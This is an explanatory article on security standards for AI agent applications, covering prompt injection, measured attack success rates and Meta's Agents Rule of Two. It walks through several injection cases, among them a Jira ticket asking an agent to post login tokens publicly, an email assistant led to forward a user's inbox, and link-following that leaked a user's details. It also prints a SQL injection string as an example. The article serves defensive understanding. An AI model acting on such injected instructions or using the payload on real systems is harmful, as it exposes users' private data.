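# Security standards for AI agent applications

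## Agentic applications and the security practice they inherit

An AI agent is software in which a language model chooses and carries out actions through tools to reach a goal. An agentic application is a product or internal system built around one or more agents, such as a coding assistant that edits files and runs tests, or a support desk that looks up orders and issues refunds. These applications read text from strangers while holding permissions that belong to somebody else, and they often act without a person approving each step. Security standards for them are the rules, lists, specifications and tests that developers and operators use to try to prevent the damage this combination can cause. Companies, practitioner groups and governments have written such standards, but as of December 2026 most are voluntary, and several are drafts or early versions.

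Nearly all security standards for AI agent applications borrow from application security, the older discipline of building and checking software that people will attack. How well its methods work for agents depends on what happens inside an agent while it runs.

### The agent loop

*Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes how Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, works, and its example illustrates how agents work in general. A user asks Codex to add an architecture diagram to the README, the file that introduces a software project. The program around the model, which Bolin calls the "harness" and others call the "host", assembles the model's input, called the prompt. The prompt contains standing instructions, definitions of the available tools, a note on which folders the agent may write to and when it must ask permission, the current working folder, and, at the end, the user's request.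 The model then produces either a reply to the user or a request for a tool call.

Here the model outputs a request that names the shell tool, which runs commands on the user's computer, and gives a command to print the README. The model can only output text, so the host program runs the command, appends the request and the result to the prompt, and sends the prompt back to the model. With the README in its context, the model can request another call, perhaps to edit the file, and the cycle repeats until the model outputs a message for the user instead. Bolin notes that a single user request could lead to hundreds of calls.

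An agent's working memory is therefore one text that keeps growing. It must fit in the context window, which Bolin defines as the maximum number of tokens (word fragments) that a model can use in one call, counting both input and output. A session is one run of an agent with one continuous context window. Anything the agent read earlier in a session can still affect what it does now. When the text grows too long, Codex compacts it by replacing the history with a shorter list of items that represents it. This makes the boundary of a session somewhat less clear, because the original text is gone but may still influence the agent. For security purposes, it seems safer to count the compacted run as the same session.

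Codex also gives each message in the prompt a role. The roles, from highest rank to lowest, are system, developer, user and assistant. The ranking guides the model, but no code stops it from acting on low-ranked content. The README's contents arrive in the same text as the user's request.

### Tools and the Model Context Protocol

A tool is a function an agent can call, such as sending an email, querying a database or running code. The model receives the tool's name, a plain-language description and a list of parameters. In Bolin's example, a weather tool takes a latitude and a longitude. Codex gets its tools from the harness itself, from OpenAI's API (web search, for one) and from whatever the user has connected. It runs its own shell tool in a sandbox, which limits access to files and the network. The sandbox does not cover tools that the user has connected from outside, which have to supply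 their own guardrails. A coding agent can therefore have both a sandboxed shell and an email tool with no guardrails.

Agents usually reach those outside tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open protocol that also connects them to data sources. Anthropic's *Introducing the Model Context Protocol* presented it as a replacement for the custom connection that developers had to write for every new data source, and the official documentation compares it to a USB-C port. The AI application, called the host, contains a client that connects to a server. The server offers tools, data or ready-made prompts, and can be anything from a small script on the user's machine to a cloud service.

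MCP has spread fast, and in the release notes for the July 2026 version, Model Context Protocol (2026), the maintainers report close to half a billion downloads a month across the main SDKs. The same release removed protocol-level sessions. Each request is now self-contained and includes its own version and client details, and a server that needs to keep state between calls gives the model an explicit handle to pass back later. Earlier advice about protecting MCP session identifiers concerns the removed mechanism and has little to do with a session in the sense of one run with one context window.

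### Prompt injection

Prompt injection is text that reaches a model as data but makes it follow an attacker's instructions. In the direct form, the attacker types the text into the application, as when a customer tells a refund agent that its rules have changed and every refund is now automatic. In the indirect form, the attacker leaves the text somewhere the agent will read it and doesn't need to use the application at all.

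*Agentic AI and Security* (2025), a guide for software engineers, retells a case of indirect prompt injection. A company tracks its work in Jira, a ticketing system, and support requests that the public files through Zendesk are automatically copied into it. An employee uses an agent to browse the Jira tickets through an MCP server. The attacker files a support request whose text asks the reader to look for long strings beginning with "eyj", the opening characters of a common kind of login token, and to record any matches in a comment on the ticket, where the public can see them.

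In the loop, the employee's question goes into the context, the model requests the ticket, and the host appends the ticket's text, including the attacker's sentences. If the model acts on those sentences, it next requests a search for tokens and then a comment. The host program carries out both because the employee's agent is authorized to read those files and comment on tickets. The attack requires no leaked password or failed access check. Security engineers have long called this kind of program a confused deputy, meaning a privileged program that someone tricks into using its authority on behalf of a person who lacks it.

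*Agentic AI and Security* attributes the problem to language models having no rigorous way to separate instructions from data, whereas a database lets programmers keep the commands in a query separate from the values. The guide quotes the security researcher Bruce Schneier, who said in 2025, "We have zero agentic AI systems that are secure against these attacks."

### What application security already had

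Application security has developed its own instruments over more than two decades, and one ordinary flaw shows what each is for. If an online shop displays invoices at a web address that ends in the invoice number, and the code never checks that the invoice belongs to the person requesting it, anyone can read a stranger's invoice by changing the number.

The best-known risk list is the OWASP Top 10, published by the Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a non-profit organisation. Trend Micro's *What are the OWASP Top 10 risks for LLMs?* describes it as a regularly updated list of the most critical risks to web applications. The shop's flaw belongs under "broken access control", which heads the list. A risk list is good for getting people's attention, but its headings are too broad to test a shop against. For testing, OWASP has the Application Security Verification Standard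 (ASVS), a long set of requirements in three levels of rigour. Each requirement is specific enough for a reviewer to say whether an application meets it.

Two naming schemes help people confirm that they are discussing the same security problem. The Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE) names types of mistake. For example, CWE-639 is letting users reach other people's records by changing a key. Common Vulnerabilities and Exposures (CVE) assigns a number to a specific flaw in a specific product. If the shop had bought its invoice software from a vendor, the vendor could announce the flaw under a CVE number, and its other customers could use that number to check whether they had the flaw too.

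*Security and Privacy Controls for Information Systems and Organizations* (SP 800-53, 2020), from the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), is a catalogue of safeguards, called controls, that an organisation selects from and an auditor can check. The shop lacks the access enforcement control, AC-3. In a penetration test, the shop would hire people to attack it and report how they got in, and a competent tester would try changing the invoice number within the first hour. In an audit, an outsider compares what an organisation does with what a document requires. In certification, a recognised body also issues a certificate vouching for the result.

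All of these apply two older principles. Least privilege, which the computer scientist Jerome Saltzer formulated in the 1970s, means giving a program only the permissions its task requires, so the invoice page can read invoices but cannot access the payroll. Defence in depth means using several independent protections on the assumption that one of them will fail.

All of this applies unchanged to agentic applications, which have the ordinary flaws of software. *Agentic AI and Security* warns that startups and hobbyists put together many MCP servers with little concern for security, and tells readers to run the usual checks on who maintains the code and how they respond to vulnerability reports. *Model Context Protocol (MCP) Security* (2026), guidance from an industry project called the Coalition for Secure AI (CoSAI), includes a heading for conventional security among its MCP threats. The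 naming schemes and the patching routine around them fit the Jira case less well, because they work best when a flaw is a mistake at an identifiable place in the code, which someone can number and fix. The ticket could deceive the agent without any such mistake. Least privilege holds up better, because it limits what a deceived agent can do, whatever the cause of the deception.

### What people mean by a "standard"

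Documents called standards differ widely in authority. Some are design rules that one company publishes for its own engineers and recommends to everyone else. Meta's Agents Rule of Two, for example, lets an unsupervised agent combine at most two of three risky properties in a session. Others are community risk lists, such as the OWASP Top 10, which records what experienced practitioners consider the worst dangers. Neither kind binds anyone outside the organisation that wrote it unless a customer puts it into a contract.

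Developers have a more practical reason to follow a technical specification, because software that departs from it will not connect. But this applies only to behaviour the other side can observe. The Model Context Protocol specification includes a security principle that hosts "must obtain explicit user consent before invoking any tool". The "must" is in lower case, and the specification's opening rules give such words their formal meaning only in capitals. A few lines later, the specification uses a capitalised SHOULD to introduce a list of advice on consent flows and access controls. The same passage states that MCP "itself cannot enforce these security principles at the protocol level", so a host can run every tool without asking for consent and still exchange valid MCP messages.

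Government guidance is also mostly advisory. NIST, for example, calls its taxonomy of attacks on AI systems voluntary. The main exception is SP 800-53, which US law requires federal agencies to apply. Agencies' contracts often require contractors to apply parts of it too, but it is optional for everyone else.

A formal standard comes from a recognised standards body, such as ISO and IEC internationally or CEN and CENELEC in Europe, after a drafting process with national delegations. It is also voluntary, but gains force when a law refers to it. Under the EU's AI Act, for example, a company that follows a European standard the EU has officially listed is presumed to meet the matching legal duty. In a certification scheme, an examiner checks whether a company meets the standard. No general law requires a company to obtain a certificate under ISO/IEC 27001, the standard for managing information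 security, but many corporate customers ask to see one before signing a contract, which can matter more to a supplier than a regulation.

### Who writes them

AI and cloud companies, including Anthropic, OpenAI, Google, Meta, Microsoft and Amazon, write design rules and specifications, usually based on experience with their own products. OWASP relies on volunteers and has run a Generative AI Security Project since May 2023. NIST writes guidelines and control catalogues, and the cyber agencies of the United States and its allies publish joint advice. Foundations manage specifications that competitors share. For example, the Linux Foundation (2025) announced that MCP had moved to its new Agentic AI Foundation, whose top-tier members include Amazon Web Services, Anthropic, Google, Microsoft and OpenAI. Some people work for several of these groups. According to OWASP AI Exchange's *AI Security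 Overview*, Rob van der Veer, who founded the AI Exchange in 2022, also works on the formal standards ISO/IEC 27090 and 27091 and on European standards for the AI Act, where the EU member states elected him co-editor. Two documents may therefore agree because the same people wrote both.

### "Super Intelligence" in American documents

On 29 September 2026, President Trump signed Executive Order 14434, which tells federal agencies to write "Super Intelligence" or "SI" instead of "artificial intelligence" or "AI" in reports, websites, policy documents and letters. The law firm Wiley Rein explains in *Executive Order Rebrands AI as "Super Intelligence"* (2026) that the order keeps the existing legal definition of AI, a machine-based system that makes predictions, recommendations or decisions for objectives that humans define. Although "superintelligence" elsewhere means a hypothetical intellect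 beyond the human, in US government documents since then it can refer to a spam filter, and "SI agent" means an AI agent.

The order does not change earlier documents, so one project can appear under two names. NIST is preparing control overlays for AI, each of which selects and adapts SP 800-53 controls for one kind of system. Two of the planned overlays deal with agents. The project began as Control Overlays for Securing AI Systems (COSAiS). NIST's *SP 800-53 Control Overlays for Super Intelligence Systems COSIS* records the change of name on 20 October 2026, and still offers a draft outline from January under the old title.

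NIST's AI centre began as the US AI Safety Institute. The U.S. Department of Commerce's *Statement from U.S. Secretary of Commerce Howard Lutnick* announced its conversion into the Center for AI Standards and Innovation (CAISI), and it is now the Center for Advancing Innovation and Standards for Super Intelligence (CAISSI). According to NIST's *Center for Advancing Innovation and Standards for Super Intelligence (CAISSI)*, the centre's tasks include developing security guidelines for SI systems and helping industry develop voluntary standards. Older evaluations still carry the CAISI name.

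The new usage is also inconsistent. *Trump's superintelligence rebrand causes confusion among federal agencies* (Giella, 2026) reports that officials are mostly complying but that both terms are in use, sometimes on the same page. For example, the State Department introduces its Pax Silica supply-chain initiative as an effort on Super Intelligence, then writes "AI" four times further down. California has ordered its own agencies to keep saying "artificial intelligence". Anyone searching for American guidance on agents should try both terms.

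## Why the usual fix for injection does not work on language models

Web developers faced injection attacks long before language models existed. Attackers typed database commands into web forms, and the databases ran them. Developers mostly solved the problem with a fix that takes little effort and works whenever a programmer applies it properly. So far nobody has found an equivalent fix for agents, because language models process text differently from databases.

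### SQL injection and its cure

SQL is the language in which programs query most databases. Suppose that an online shop lets customers look up an invoice by its reference. The shop's code writes the start of a query, pastes in whatever the customer typed, and adds a closing quotation mark. When customer 17 types A-1024, the database receives this and returns one invoice:

```
SELECT * FROM invoices WHERE customer = 17 AND reference = 'A-1024'
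```

An attacker types `x' OR '1'='1` into the same box, and the same code produces this:

```
SELECT * FROM invoices WHERE customer = 17 AND reference = 'x' OR '1'='1'
```

The quotation mark after the x closes the reference early, so the database treats the rest as part of the command. Since '1' always equals '1', the condition after OR is true for every row, and the attacker gets every customer's invoices.

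In a parameterised query, the programmer writes the command with empty slots and sends the values separately:

```
SELECT * FROM invoices WHERE customer = ? AND reference = ?
first value:   17
second value:  x' OR '1'='1
```

The database parses the command before it fills the slots, so what goes into them cannot change the command's structure. The second slot can only hold a value to compare with the reference column. Quotation marks have a special meaning only during parsing, so the database treats the ones in `x' OR '1'='1` as ordinary characters. It looks for an invoice with that exact string as its reference, finds none, and returns nothing.

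This protection works even against attacks nobody has thought of yet, because it doesn't depend on recognising them. The shop therefore doesn't need to try thousands of hostile inputs. But slots can only hold values. If a programmer pastes a customer's text into the command itself, for instance as the name of a column to sort by, injection becomes possible again. That mistake is in a particular line of code, where a reviewer can find it.

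The web was slow to adopt this fix, even though it works so well. SQL injection dates from the 1990s and peaked around 2010, and it took a decade of breaches to bring in safer defaults, according to *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*. David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), wrote the post in December 2025 because many experienced web security people seemed to assume that prompt injection was the same sort of problem.

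### One stream of tokens

David C gives the example of a recruitment tool that instructs a model to score whether a CV meets the job's requirements, then gives it the CV. The candidate has hidden a line in the CV telling the system to approve it. The model receives the instruction and the CV as one sequence of tokens. It calculates from the whole sequence which token is likely to come next, adds that token, and repeats. This process has no equivalent of the database's parsing step, which settles what the command is before any data arrives.

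Developers can label the parts of the model's input, as Codex does with its message roles, and a host program can strip fake labels out of a document before the model receives it. Training makes models give more weight to text labelled as the developer's or the user's. But the model processes the label together with the text, so the label only lowers the chance that the model will follow a sentence in the CV, whereas a parameterised query prevents the database from running the text in its slot as a command.

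Even a better architecture might not solve the problem, because it is hard to define how instructions and data should be separated. An invoice reference should never act as a command, but people ask agents to follow the setup steps in a README or deal with whatever their manager's latest email asks for. In these cases, outside text has to influence what the agent does, and the agent has to distinguish the influence its user wants from the influence an attacker wants.

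Researchers are working on ways to detect injection attempts, train models to prioritize instructions over anything in the data, and mark the data more clearly. David C thinks all of these impose a distinction between instructions and data on a technology that doesn't have one, and that developers may therefore never be able to eliminate prompt injection as they can SQL injection.

### The "inherently confusable deputy"

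He suggests thinking of prompt injection as a confused deputy problem instead. The programmer Norm Hardy introduced the term in 1988 with a story about a compiler. The compiler had permission to write to the system folder where it kept its usage statistics, and the billing records were in the same folder. A user who had no permission to change the billing file told the compiler to save output under that file's name, and the compiler overwrote the bills.

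The compiler could be fixed by having it open any file a user names with that user's permissions and use its own permissions only for the statistics. David C argues that a language model is an "inherently confusable deputy" that can't be fixed this way. Designers should expect it to be deceived sometimes and limit the damage that can result. In his account, the worst case for an injected agent is whatever an attacker could do with direct access to its tools.

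Most of David C's advice follows from this. Ordinary code, not the model, should constrain the agent's actions, as in CaMeL, a design from Google and ETH Zurich. He also likes a rule from an online exchange between the developers Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista, that a model should have only a person's privileges while it processes that person's text. In the Jira case, the employee's agent would have dropped to the privileges of a member of the public when it opened the attacker's ticket, and could not have searched the company's files for login tokens even if it had been deceived. He also recommends logging failed tool calls, since an attacker will probably need several tries. He is wary of any product that claims to stop prompt injection, and of filters that block known phrases, because attackers can reword an attack in endless ways. If a system cannot tolerate the remaining risk, he says,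 it may be a poor use for a language model.

If training and filters make successful injections rare enough, most users may not mind the lack of a guarantee. Banks tolerate some card fraud, and email providers let some spam through. Whether this is realistic for injection depends on how often attacks succeed, and measured success rates vary a great deal with how hard the testers try.

### Known attacks and new ones

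Many of the measurements use AgentDojo, a benchmark from ETH Zurich that simulates an office workspace, a travel service, a Slack chat system and a bank, and gives the agent tools for each. The agent receives a legitimate task from its user, but some of the data it reads contains instructions to do something harmful. The attack succeeds if the agent completes the harmful task. According to Inspect Evals' *AgentDojo*, the benchmark also measures how well the agent does its legitimate task. This matters because an agent that refused to read any data would resist these attacks but be useless.

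*Strengthening AI Agent Hijacking Evaluations*, published in January 2025 by the NIST centre later known as CAISI, describes AgentDojo tests on Claude 3.5 Sonnet. The model is now long out of date, but it was then among the models that best resisted AgentDojo's attacks. The strongest existing attack succeeded 11% of the time. The centre's staff and red-teamers (people who attack a system to test it) from the UK AI Security Institute then wrote new attacks for this model, using some of the workspace tasks, and measured them on other workspace tasks that they had held back. The best new attack succeeded 81% of the time. The new attacks also did well in the other three environments, which the red-teamers had not used to develop them.

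*The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) tested 12 published defences, some against prompt injection and some against users who try to get forbidden answers out of a model. Most of the defences had been published with reported attack success rates near zero. Nasr and colleagues attacked each defence with automated methods that try a text, score the result and improve on it. They adapted these methods to each defence and gave them plenty of computing power. They also ran an online contest with more than 500 human attackers.

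Attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the defences. Two of the defences rely on wording. One marks which text to trust, and the other repeats the user's request after the untrusted text. They had held the success rate of known attacks to as little as 1% on AgentDojo, but the adaptive attack succeeded more than 95% of the time against both. The attack success rate against Meta SecAlign, a model trained to resist injection, rose from 2% to 96%. Filters are separate models that classify text as safe or suspicious. Three of the four tested let through more than 90% of attacks, and the fourth let through 71%. Stacking several filters didn't solve the problem. On a subset of the scenarios, the automated search succeeded 69% of the time, while the human attackers as a group succeeded every time.

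These numbers probably overstate what an ordinary criminal could achieve. The automated attack had access to a filter's confidence score after each try, and Nasr and colleagues deliberately ignored the resources an attack requires, which matter a lot if the aim is a tolerable level of risk. Filters are easy to install and stop unsophisticated attackers, so Nasr and colleagues call them "useful—but limited". But the study does undermine the practice of reporting a low attack success rate on a fixed list of old attacks as evidence of security.

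### A public competition

In late 2025, the security firm Gray Swan worked with the UK AI Security Institute and several AI developers to run a public competition in hijacking AI agents. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports that 464 participants made 271,588 attempts against 13 models. The scenarios covered agents that call tools, write code, or operate a computer through its screen. In each scenario, the participant controlled one piece of the data the agent would read. In most scenarios, an attempt counted as a success only if the agent carried out the harmful action and its final reply gave the user no sign of it.

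Participants succeeded 8,648 times, or in about 3% of attempts. CAISI's *Insights into AI Agent Security from a Large-Scale Red-Teaming Competition* stresses that every model was successfully attacked at least once, but success rates ranged from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro. Participants successfully attacked Gemini in all 37 scenarios of the main rounds and Opus in 13. General capability, as measured by a hard science test, had only a weak and statistically insignificant correlation with attack success rate. Dziemian and colleagues think the developer's training method matters more.

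Participants could read the whole conversation in advance and knew exactly which action they had to cause, advantages that real attackers seldom have. But they had only one message, and the concealment rule excluded attacks that did harm openly. Claude Opus 4.5 and GPT-5 carried out the harmful action in roughly 1% to 3% of cases, which is higher than their headline rates and probably the more relevant figure for an irreversible payment. Staff from Anthropic, OpenAI and Meta are among the co-authors, although participants saw the models only under random code names.

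Gray Swan has repeated the competition several times, most recently in August 2026 according to the *Beam Model Technical Report* (2026) from the AI company Reflection. Gray Swan has also begun a bug bounty that pays people for successful injections against agents as companies deploy them.

### From one attempt to many

A rate of 0.5% or 1% sounds small, but an attacker who fails can usually try again. If each try succeeds with probability p, and the tries are independent, the chance that k tries all fail is (1 − p)^k. The chance of at least one success is therefore

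1 − (1 − p)^k

If each try has a 1% chance of success, an attacker who makes 100 tries has a 63% chance of getting through at least once, since (0.99)^100 is about 0.37. If better training cuts the success rate to 0.1% per try, the chance over 100 tries falls to about 10%, but it returns to 63% over 1,000 tries. When a try takes no more effort than sending an email, attackers may soon offset a tenfold improvement in the model by trying ten times as often.

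Real attempts are not independent, though, so the formula can be badly wrong. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reports that strong attacks from a Gray Swan benchmark succeeded against that model 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten, and 63% with a hundred. From the 4.7% rate, the formula predicts 38% for ten attempts, which is close, and 99% for a hundred, which is far too high. Similarly, in CAISI's experiment of January 2025, the average success rate over five harmful tasks rose from 57% on one attempt to 80% after 25, when independence would have made success practically certain.

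This is probably because the average combines easy and hard targets. Suppose an agent is vulnerable in half of its tasks, where each try succeeds 2% of the time, and safe in the other half. The average success rate is still 1%, so the formula gives a 63% chance of at least one success in 100 tries. The true chance on a randomly chosen task is 43%, because the attack can never work on half of the tasks. Any such mixture makes the true figure lower than the formula's.

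An attacker who learns from earlier attempts does better on the fiftieth try than on the first. In the competition, successes rose roughly in line with attempts and showed no sign of levelling off. One attack text, with only small changes of wording, worked in 21 scenarios and on nine models. When Dziemian and colleagues re-ran 44 attacks made against Claude Opus 4.5 on the other models, the attacks succeeded 44% to 81% of the time on each. Attacks that had beaten the weakest models almost never worked on Opus. Since thousands of companies may run agents on the same model, a text that works on one agent will probably work on many others, and the damage could happen all at once.

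An operator can also influence the number of tries, which is the point of David C's advice about failed tool calls. If the operator notices the third failed attempt and blocks the sender, k stays at three.

### The system cards of 2026

Developers publish a system card, a long report on abilities and safety tests, with each major model, and some cards now include attack success rates. In Anthropic's February 2026 card for Claude Opus 4.6, the rate depended heavily on what the agent was doing. VentureBeat reports that all 200 attempts failed in a restricted coding environment. Against an agent that worked through a graphical interface, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time, and the chance that at least one of 200 attempts succeeded was 78.6%, or 57.1% with extra safeguards.

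VentureBeat reports that an adaptive attack tool from Gray Swan succeeded on 7.03% of single attempts against a coding agent running the later Opus 4.8, and on 2.09% with safeguards. The test had probably become harder, since the newer model is unlikely to be so much easier to deceive than an earlier one that scored 0%. This makes it risky to infer a trend from numbers in different system cards.

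The comparison between Opus 4.8 and Opus 5, which Anthropic released in July 2026, is cleaner. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that the attack success rate after 15 attempts on a Gray Swan test fell from 5.5% to 2.0%. For browser agents in Anthropic's own software, it was zero across 129 scenarios. ClawSouls' *The most exciting line was buried in a system card* quotes Boris Cherny, who leads work on Anthropic's coding agent, as writing that the rate falls to "~0" when the company combines the model's training with injection detectors and the agent's automatic permission checks. Bruce Schneier said in 2025 that no agentic system was secure against these attacks. In 2026, he published *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* on his blog, Schneier on Security.

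OpenAI's results for GPT-6 Sol, from October 2026, are similar. *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense* (Cross, 2026) reports that the model withstood 99.99% of direct injections and 97.13% of indirect ones, the kind that agents meet in emails and web pages. About one indirect attack in 35 succeeded. These figures come from a different test than Gray Swan's, so they can't be used to rank the two companies. In November 2026, both companies released newer models, Anthropic's Claude Fable 5.2 and OpenAI's GPT-6.2.

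The optimists therefore have a much better case than when David C wrote. His remark that the risk cannot be mitigated now seems too strong if it means that training and filters achieve little, but he still seems right that there is no guarantee of the kind a parameterised query gives. Zero successes in 129 scenarios is statistically compatible with a true success rate of up to about 2%, even if future attackers are no better than the testers. As Nasr and colleagues point out, failing to break a defence in a test of this kind does not prove it sound. The best results also come from companies testing their own products with every safeguard on, and a business that builds its own agent on the same model may not have all of those safeguards.

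Whether a 2% attack success rate after 15 attempts is tolerable depends on what the agent can do. It is surely tolerable for an agent that sorts newsletters. But if companies use agents to pay invoices that arrive by email, an attacker could send 15 messages to each of a thousand companies in a morning and obtain about twenty fraudulent payments. This is why design rules such as Meta's Agents Rule of Two restrict what an unsupervised agent can do, however well its model scores.

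## The Agents Rule of Two

On 31 October 2025, Meta published a design rule for developers who want to release agents before anyone can reliably filter out prompt injection. The rule limits which abilities an unsupervised agent may have at the same time, so an attacker who deceives the model still can't do the worst kinds of damage. Meta adapted it from a rule for browser engineers and a warning by the developer Simon Willison.

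### Origins

The developers of Chromium, the open-source project behind Google's Chrome browser, have had a "Rule of 2" since 2019. Chromium's *The Rule Of 2* tells engineers to combine no more than two of untrustworthy inputs, an unsafe programming language, and high privilege. Almost everything a browser reads from the internet is untrustworthy. In an unsafe language such as C++, a programming mistake can corrupt the program's memory, which attackers can often exploit to run their own code. Code with high privilege can do anything the computer's user can. If code has all three, an attacker could use a malformed image to take control of the computer.

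Chrome's security team generally refuses to approve new code that combines all three. An engineer can comply by rewriting the code in a safe language such as Rust, running it in a sandbox, or accepting only data that provably comes from a trusted company. The engineer can also simplify the input. For example, a sandboxed process can decode a PNG image and pass only a plain grid of pixels to the privileged process. Chromium's developers admit that some existing code still breaks the rule, and their priority is to prevent new violations.

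In June 2025, *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) described a similar combination, warning that attackers can easily steal data from an agent that can see private data, reads untrusted text, and can send information out. For example, an attacker might email a user's assistant and ask it to forward the user's password reset messages, then delete them. A single connection can provide all three abilities. GitHub's MCP server let an agent read public issues that anyone could write, read private code, and publish changes where outsiders could see them.

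The trifecta covers only data theft. If an attacker tricks an agent into deleting a database, no data leaves the company, but the damage may be worse. In August 2025, as Willison (2025) relates in *The Rule Of 2*, Alex Russell pointed out to him how much the trifecta resembled Chromium's rule. Meta then credited both and widened the last property to include harmful actions. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) says that an agent should have no more than two of these properties within a session:

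- A: it can process untrustworthy inputs.
- B: it can access sensitive systems or private data.
- C: it can change state or communicate externally.

Changing state means altering something outside the conversation, such as a file, a booking or a bank balance. If a task needs all three properties and the agent can't start a new session with a fresh context window, Meta says the agent must not act autonomously and needs supervision, through human approval or "another reliable means of validation". The rule applies until researchers find a way to reliably detect and refuse prompt injection.

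The agent version is harder to follow than Chromium's. Browser engineers can often switch to a memory-safe language without removing any features. Because no language model is safe in the same way, agent developers have to restrict what the agent reads, what it can access, or what it does.

### The Email-Bot attack

Meta's main example is Email-Bot, a hypothetical assistant that summarises new mail, searches the inbox for context, and sends replies. An attacker sends a spam email containing instructions to collect the private contents of the inbox and forward them. Email-Bot reads the spam, gathers the messages, and calls its tool for sending email. Each step depends on a different property, so a developer can stop the attack at any of the three steps.

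The developer can let Email-Bot process mail only from trustworthy senders, such as close friends. Ordinary code would have to discard the spam before it reaches the model. This keeps the attacker's text out of the context window, but the user gets no help with mail from strangers. An attacker who hacks a friend's account could still get an injection through.

Alternatively, the developer can remove the private data, for instance by running Email-Bot in a test environment. The attacker may still take control of the agent but will find no private data to steal. This is fine for training or testing, but an inbox assistant needs access to the user's real email to do its job.

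The remaining option is to let Email-Bot write only to trusted recipients or require it to show each new draft to a person. It can still read everything, and an attacker may still distort its summaries, but the attacker cannot use it to send stolen messages out. For most users this is probably the least disruptive choice.

A security practitioner's notes on Meta's post, also titled *Agents Rule of Two* (2025), point out that the inbox in the Email-Bot example is both the private data the bot needs to protect and the place where spam arrives. A developer who wants to keep the private data and exclude the spam needs a reliable way to tell them apart.

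### Three more agents

Meta applies the rule to three other hypothetical agents. One, a travel assistant, searches the web and has access to the user's private details, so Meta restricts its actions. A person confirms every reservation or payment, and the assistant may open only web addresses that come from trusted sources, not ones it constructs itself. Addresses are restricted because they can carry data. If an attacker gets the agent to open a page whose address ends in the user's name, the attacker's server records the name.

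Anthropic's Claude had a similar restriction, but a small gap defeated it. Willison (2026) explains that Claude's tool for fetching web pages could open only addresses that the user had typed or a search had returned, except that it also followed links inside pages it had already fetched. Ayush Paul built a website with a link for each letter of the alphabet and told Claude to find the user's profile by spelling out the user's name. Claude followed the links letter by letter, and Paul extracted the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic has since stopped the tool from following such links.

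Meta's browsing assistant does research on the open web, where it fills in forms and sends requests to arbitrary addresses. Meta keeps it away from private data by running the browser in a sandbox where the user isn't logged in to anything. A few days before Meta's post, OpenAI added a "logged out mode" to its Atlas browser for similar reasons.

The third agent writes and runs code across a company's internal systems, including some production systems. It needs access to these systems and the ability to change them, so Meta restricts what it reads. A filter admits only data from acceptable authors, and people review items it wrongly excludes. According to the practitioner's notes, this is probably not easy, because most code changes carry no cryptographic signature to prove who wrote them. Chromium requires such proof before its engineers may trust a source, and an agent developer who relies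 on author names alone has a much weaker guarantee.

An agent can also change its combination of properties during a session. In Meta's example, the agent starts by browsing the internet without access to anything private, then makes a one-way switch that gives it access to internal systems but removes its ability to communicate. The switch has to be one-way because the web pages stay in the context. If the agent could send messages again, an instruction on a page it read earlier could make it send out what it had learned from the internal systems. Meta leaves out most of the details, but an agent that can damage the internal systems would presumably have to lose its write access too.

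### Harm without private data

In *New prompt injection papers* (Willison, 2025), Willison called the rule the best practical advice available while no reliable defence exists. Meta's diagram showed the properties as three overlapping circles. Conffab's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) preserves the original description, in which every overlap of two circles was labelled "Safe". Willison soon objected that an agent with untrusted input and the power to change things can do harm even if it has no private data.

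Mick Ayzenberg, a security researcher at Meta, replied that access to any sensitive system counts under the second property, even if the system holds no private data. An agent without that property can freely write to and communicate with other systems, but only those that don't matter for the user's security. Meta also changed the label from "Safe" to "Lower risk".

The reply answers the objection, but it makes the rule stricter than the slogan suggests. A tool that pays invoices gives an agent both access to a sensitive system and the power to change state, so the agent already has two of the three properties, and adding untrusted input breaks the rule. For harmful actions, the rule therefore means that an unsupervised agent that reads untrusted input should not be able to change anything important. Developers have three separate properties to choose from only when the danger is data theft.

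### Matters of degree

A developer has to decide whether an agent has each property, and the answer is often unclear. A company's customer database seems internal, but it may contain feedback that strangers typed into a web form. Databricks, a data platform company, advises developers to trace data to its source and ask whether an outsider could have influenced any part of it, including comments, metadata and attachments. A lot of ordinary business data is untrustworthy by that test.

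External communication can be just as hard to recognise. Microsoft's Copilot Cowork could send messages to the user's own inbox without approval. Willison reports that those messages could contain images hosted elsewhere. When the user opened a message, the mail program fetched the image, which could leak data to an attacker.

The practitioner's notes also raise the question of whether an agent changes state when it writes to its own memory. An agent might read a hostile web page, save a note, and start a new session. The context window is empty at first, but the attacker's text may return when the agent reads its note. A developer who counts properties per session would miss this. It seems safest to treat anything an agent saved after reading untrusted text as untrusted input to later sessions.

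The properties also don't measure how much damage an attack could do. An agent that can see one calendar and one that can see every medical record in a hospital both count as having access to private data. A yes-or-no rule is easier to apply consistently than a risk score, but a team still has to judge which agents need more protection than the rule requires.

### Agents that need all three

Databricks based a security guide on the Agents Rule of Two and agrees that removing one property is the most effective defence. But it says that most agents need some degree of all three, so the guide mainly covers ways to restrict each one. The guide's example, Social Gauge, reads social media posts, combines them with customer records, and writes the results to company tables.

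Under the guide, Social Gauge acts with the permissions of the employee using it, so a deceived agent can reach only what that employee could. Network rules block outgoing connections except to approved destinations. A separate model screens the text for attacks, and Databricks reports that such screening cut successful attacks by more than 90%. But the test used known attacks from a public scanner, and Nasr and colleagues found that filters that stop known attacks often fail against attackers who adapt. The network and permission limits seem more dependable because they don't rely on recognising an attack.

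This is a reasonable way to run a useful agent, but under Meta's rule, an agent that retains all three properties in weaker form would still need supervision. Meta concedes that the rule fits some desirable agents poorly, such as background processes where stopping to ask a person would be disruptive or ineffective.

### Human approval

When an agent has all three properties, its security may depend on whether a person reads what they approve. The evidence from 2026 is discouraging. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users approve 97% of the permission prompts in Claude Code, the company's coding agent. Anthropic's earlier post, *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, put the figure at 93%. Most prompts concern routine commands, so a high approval rate doesn't prove carelessness.

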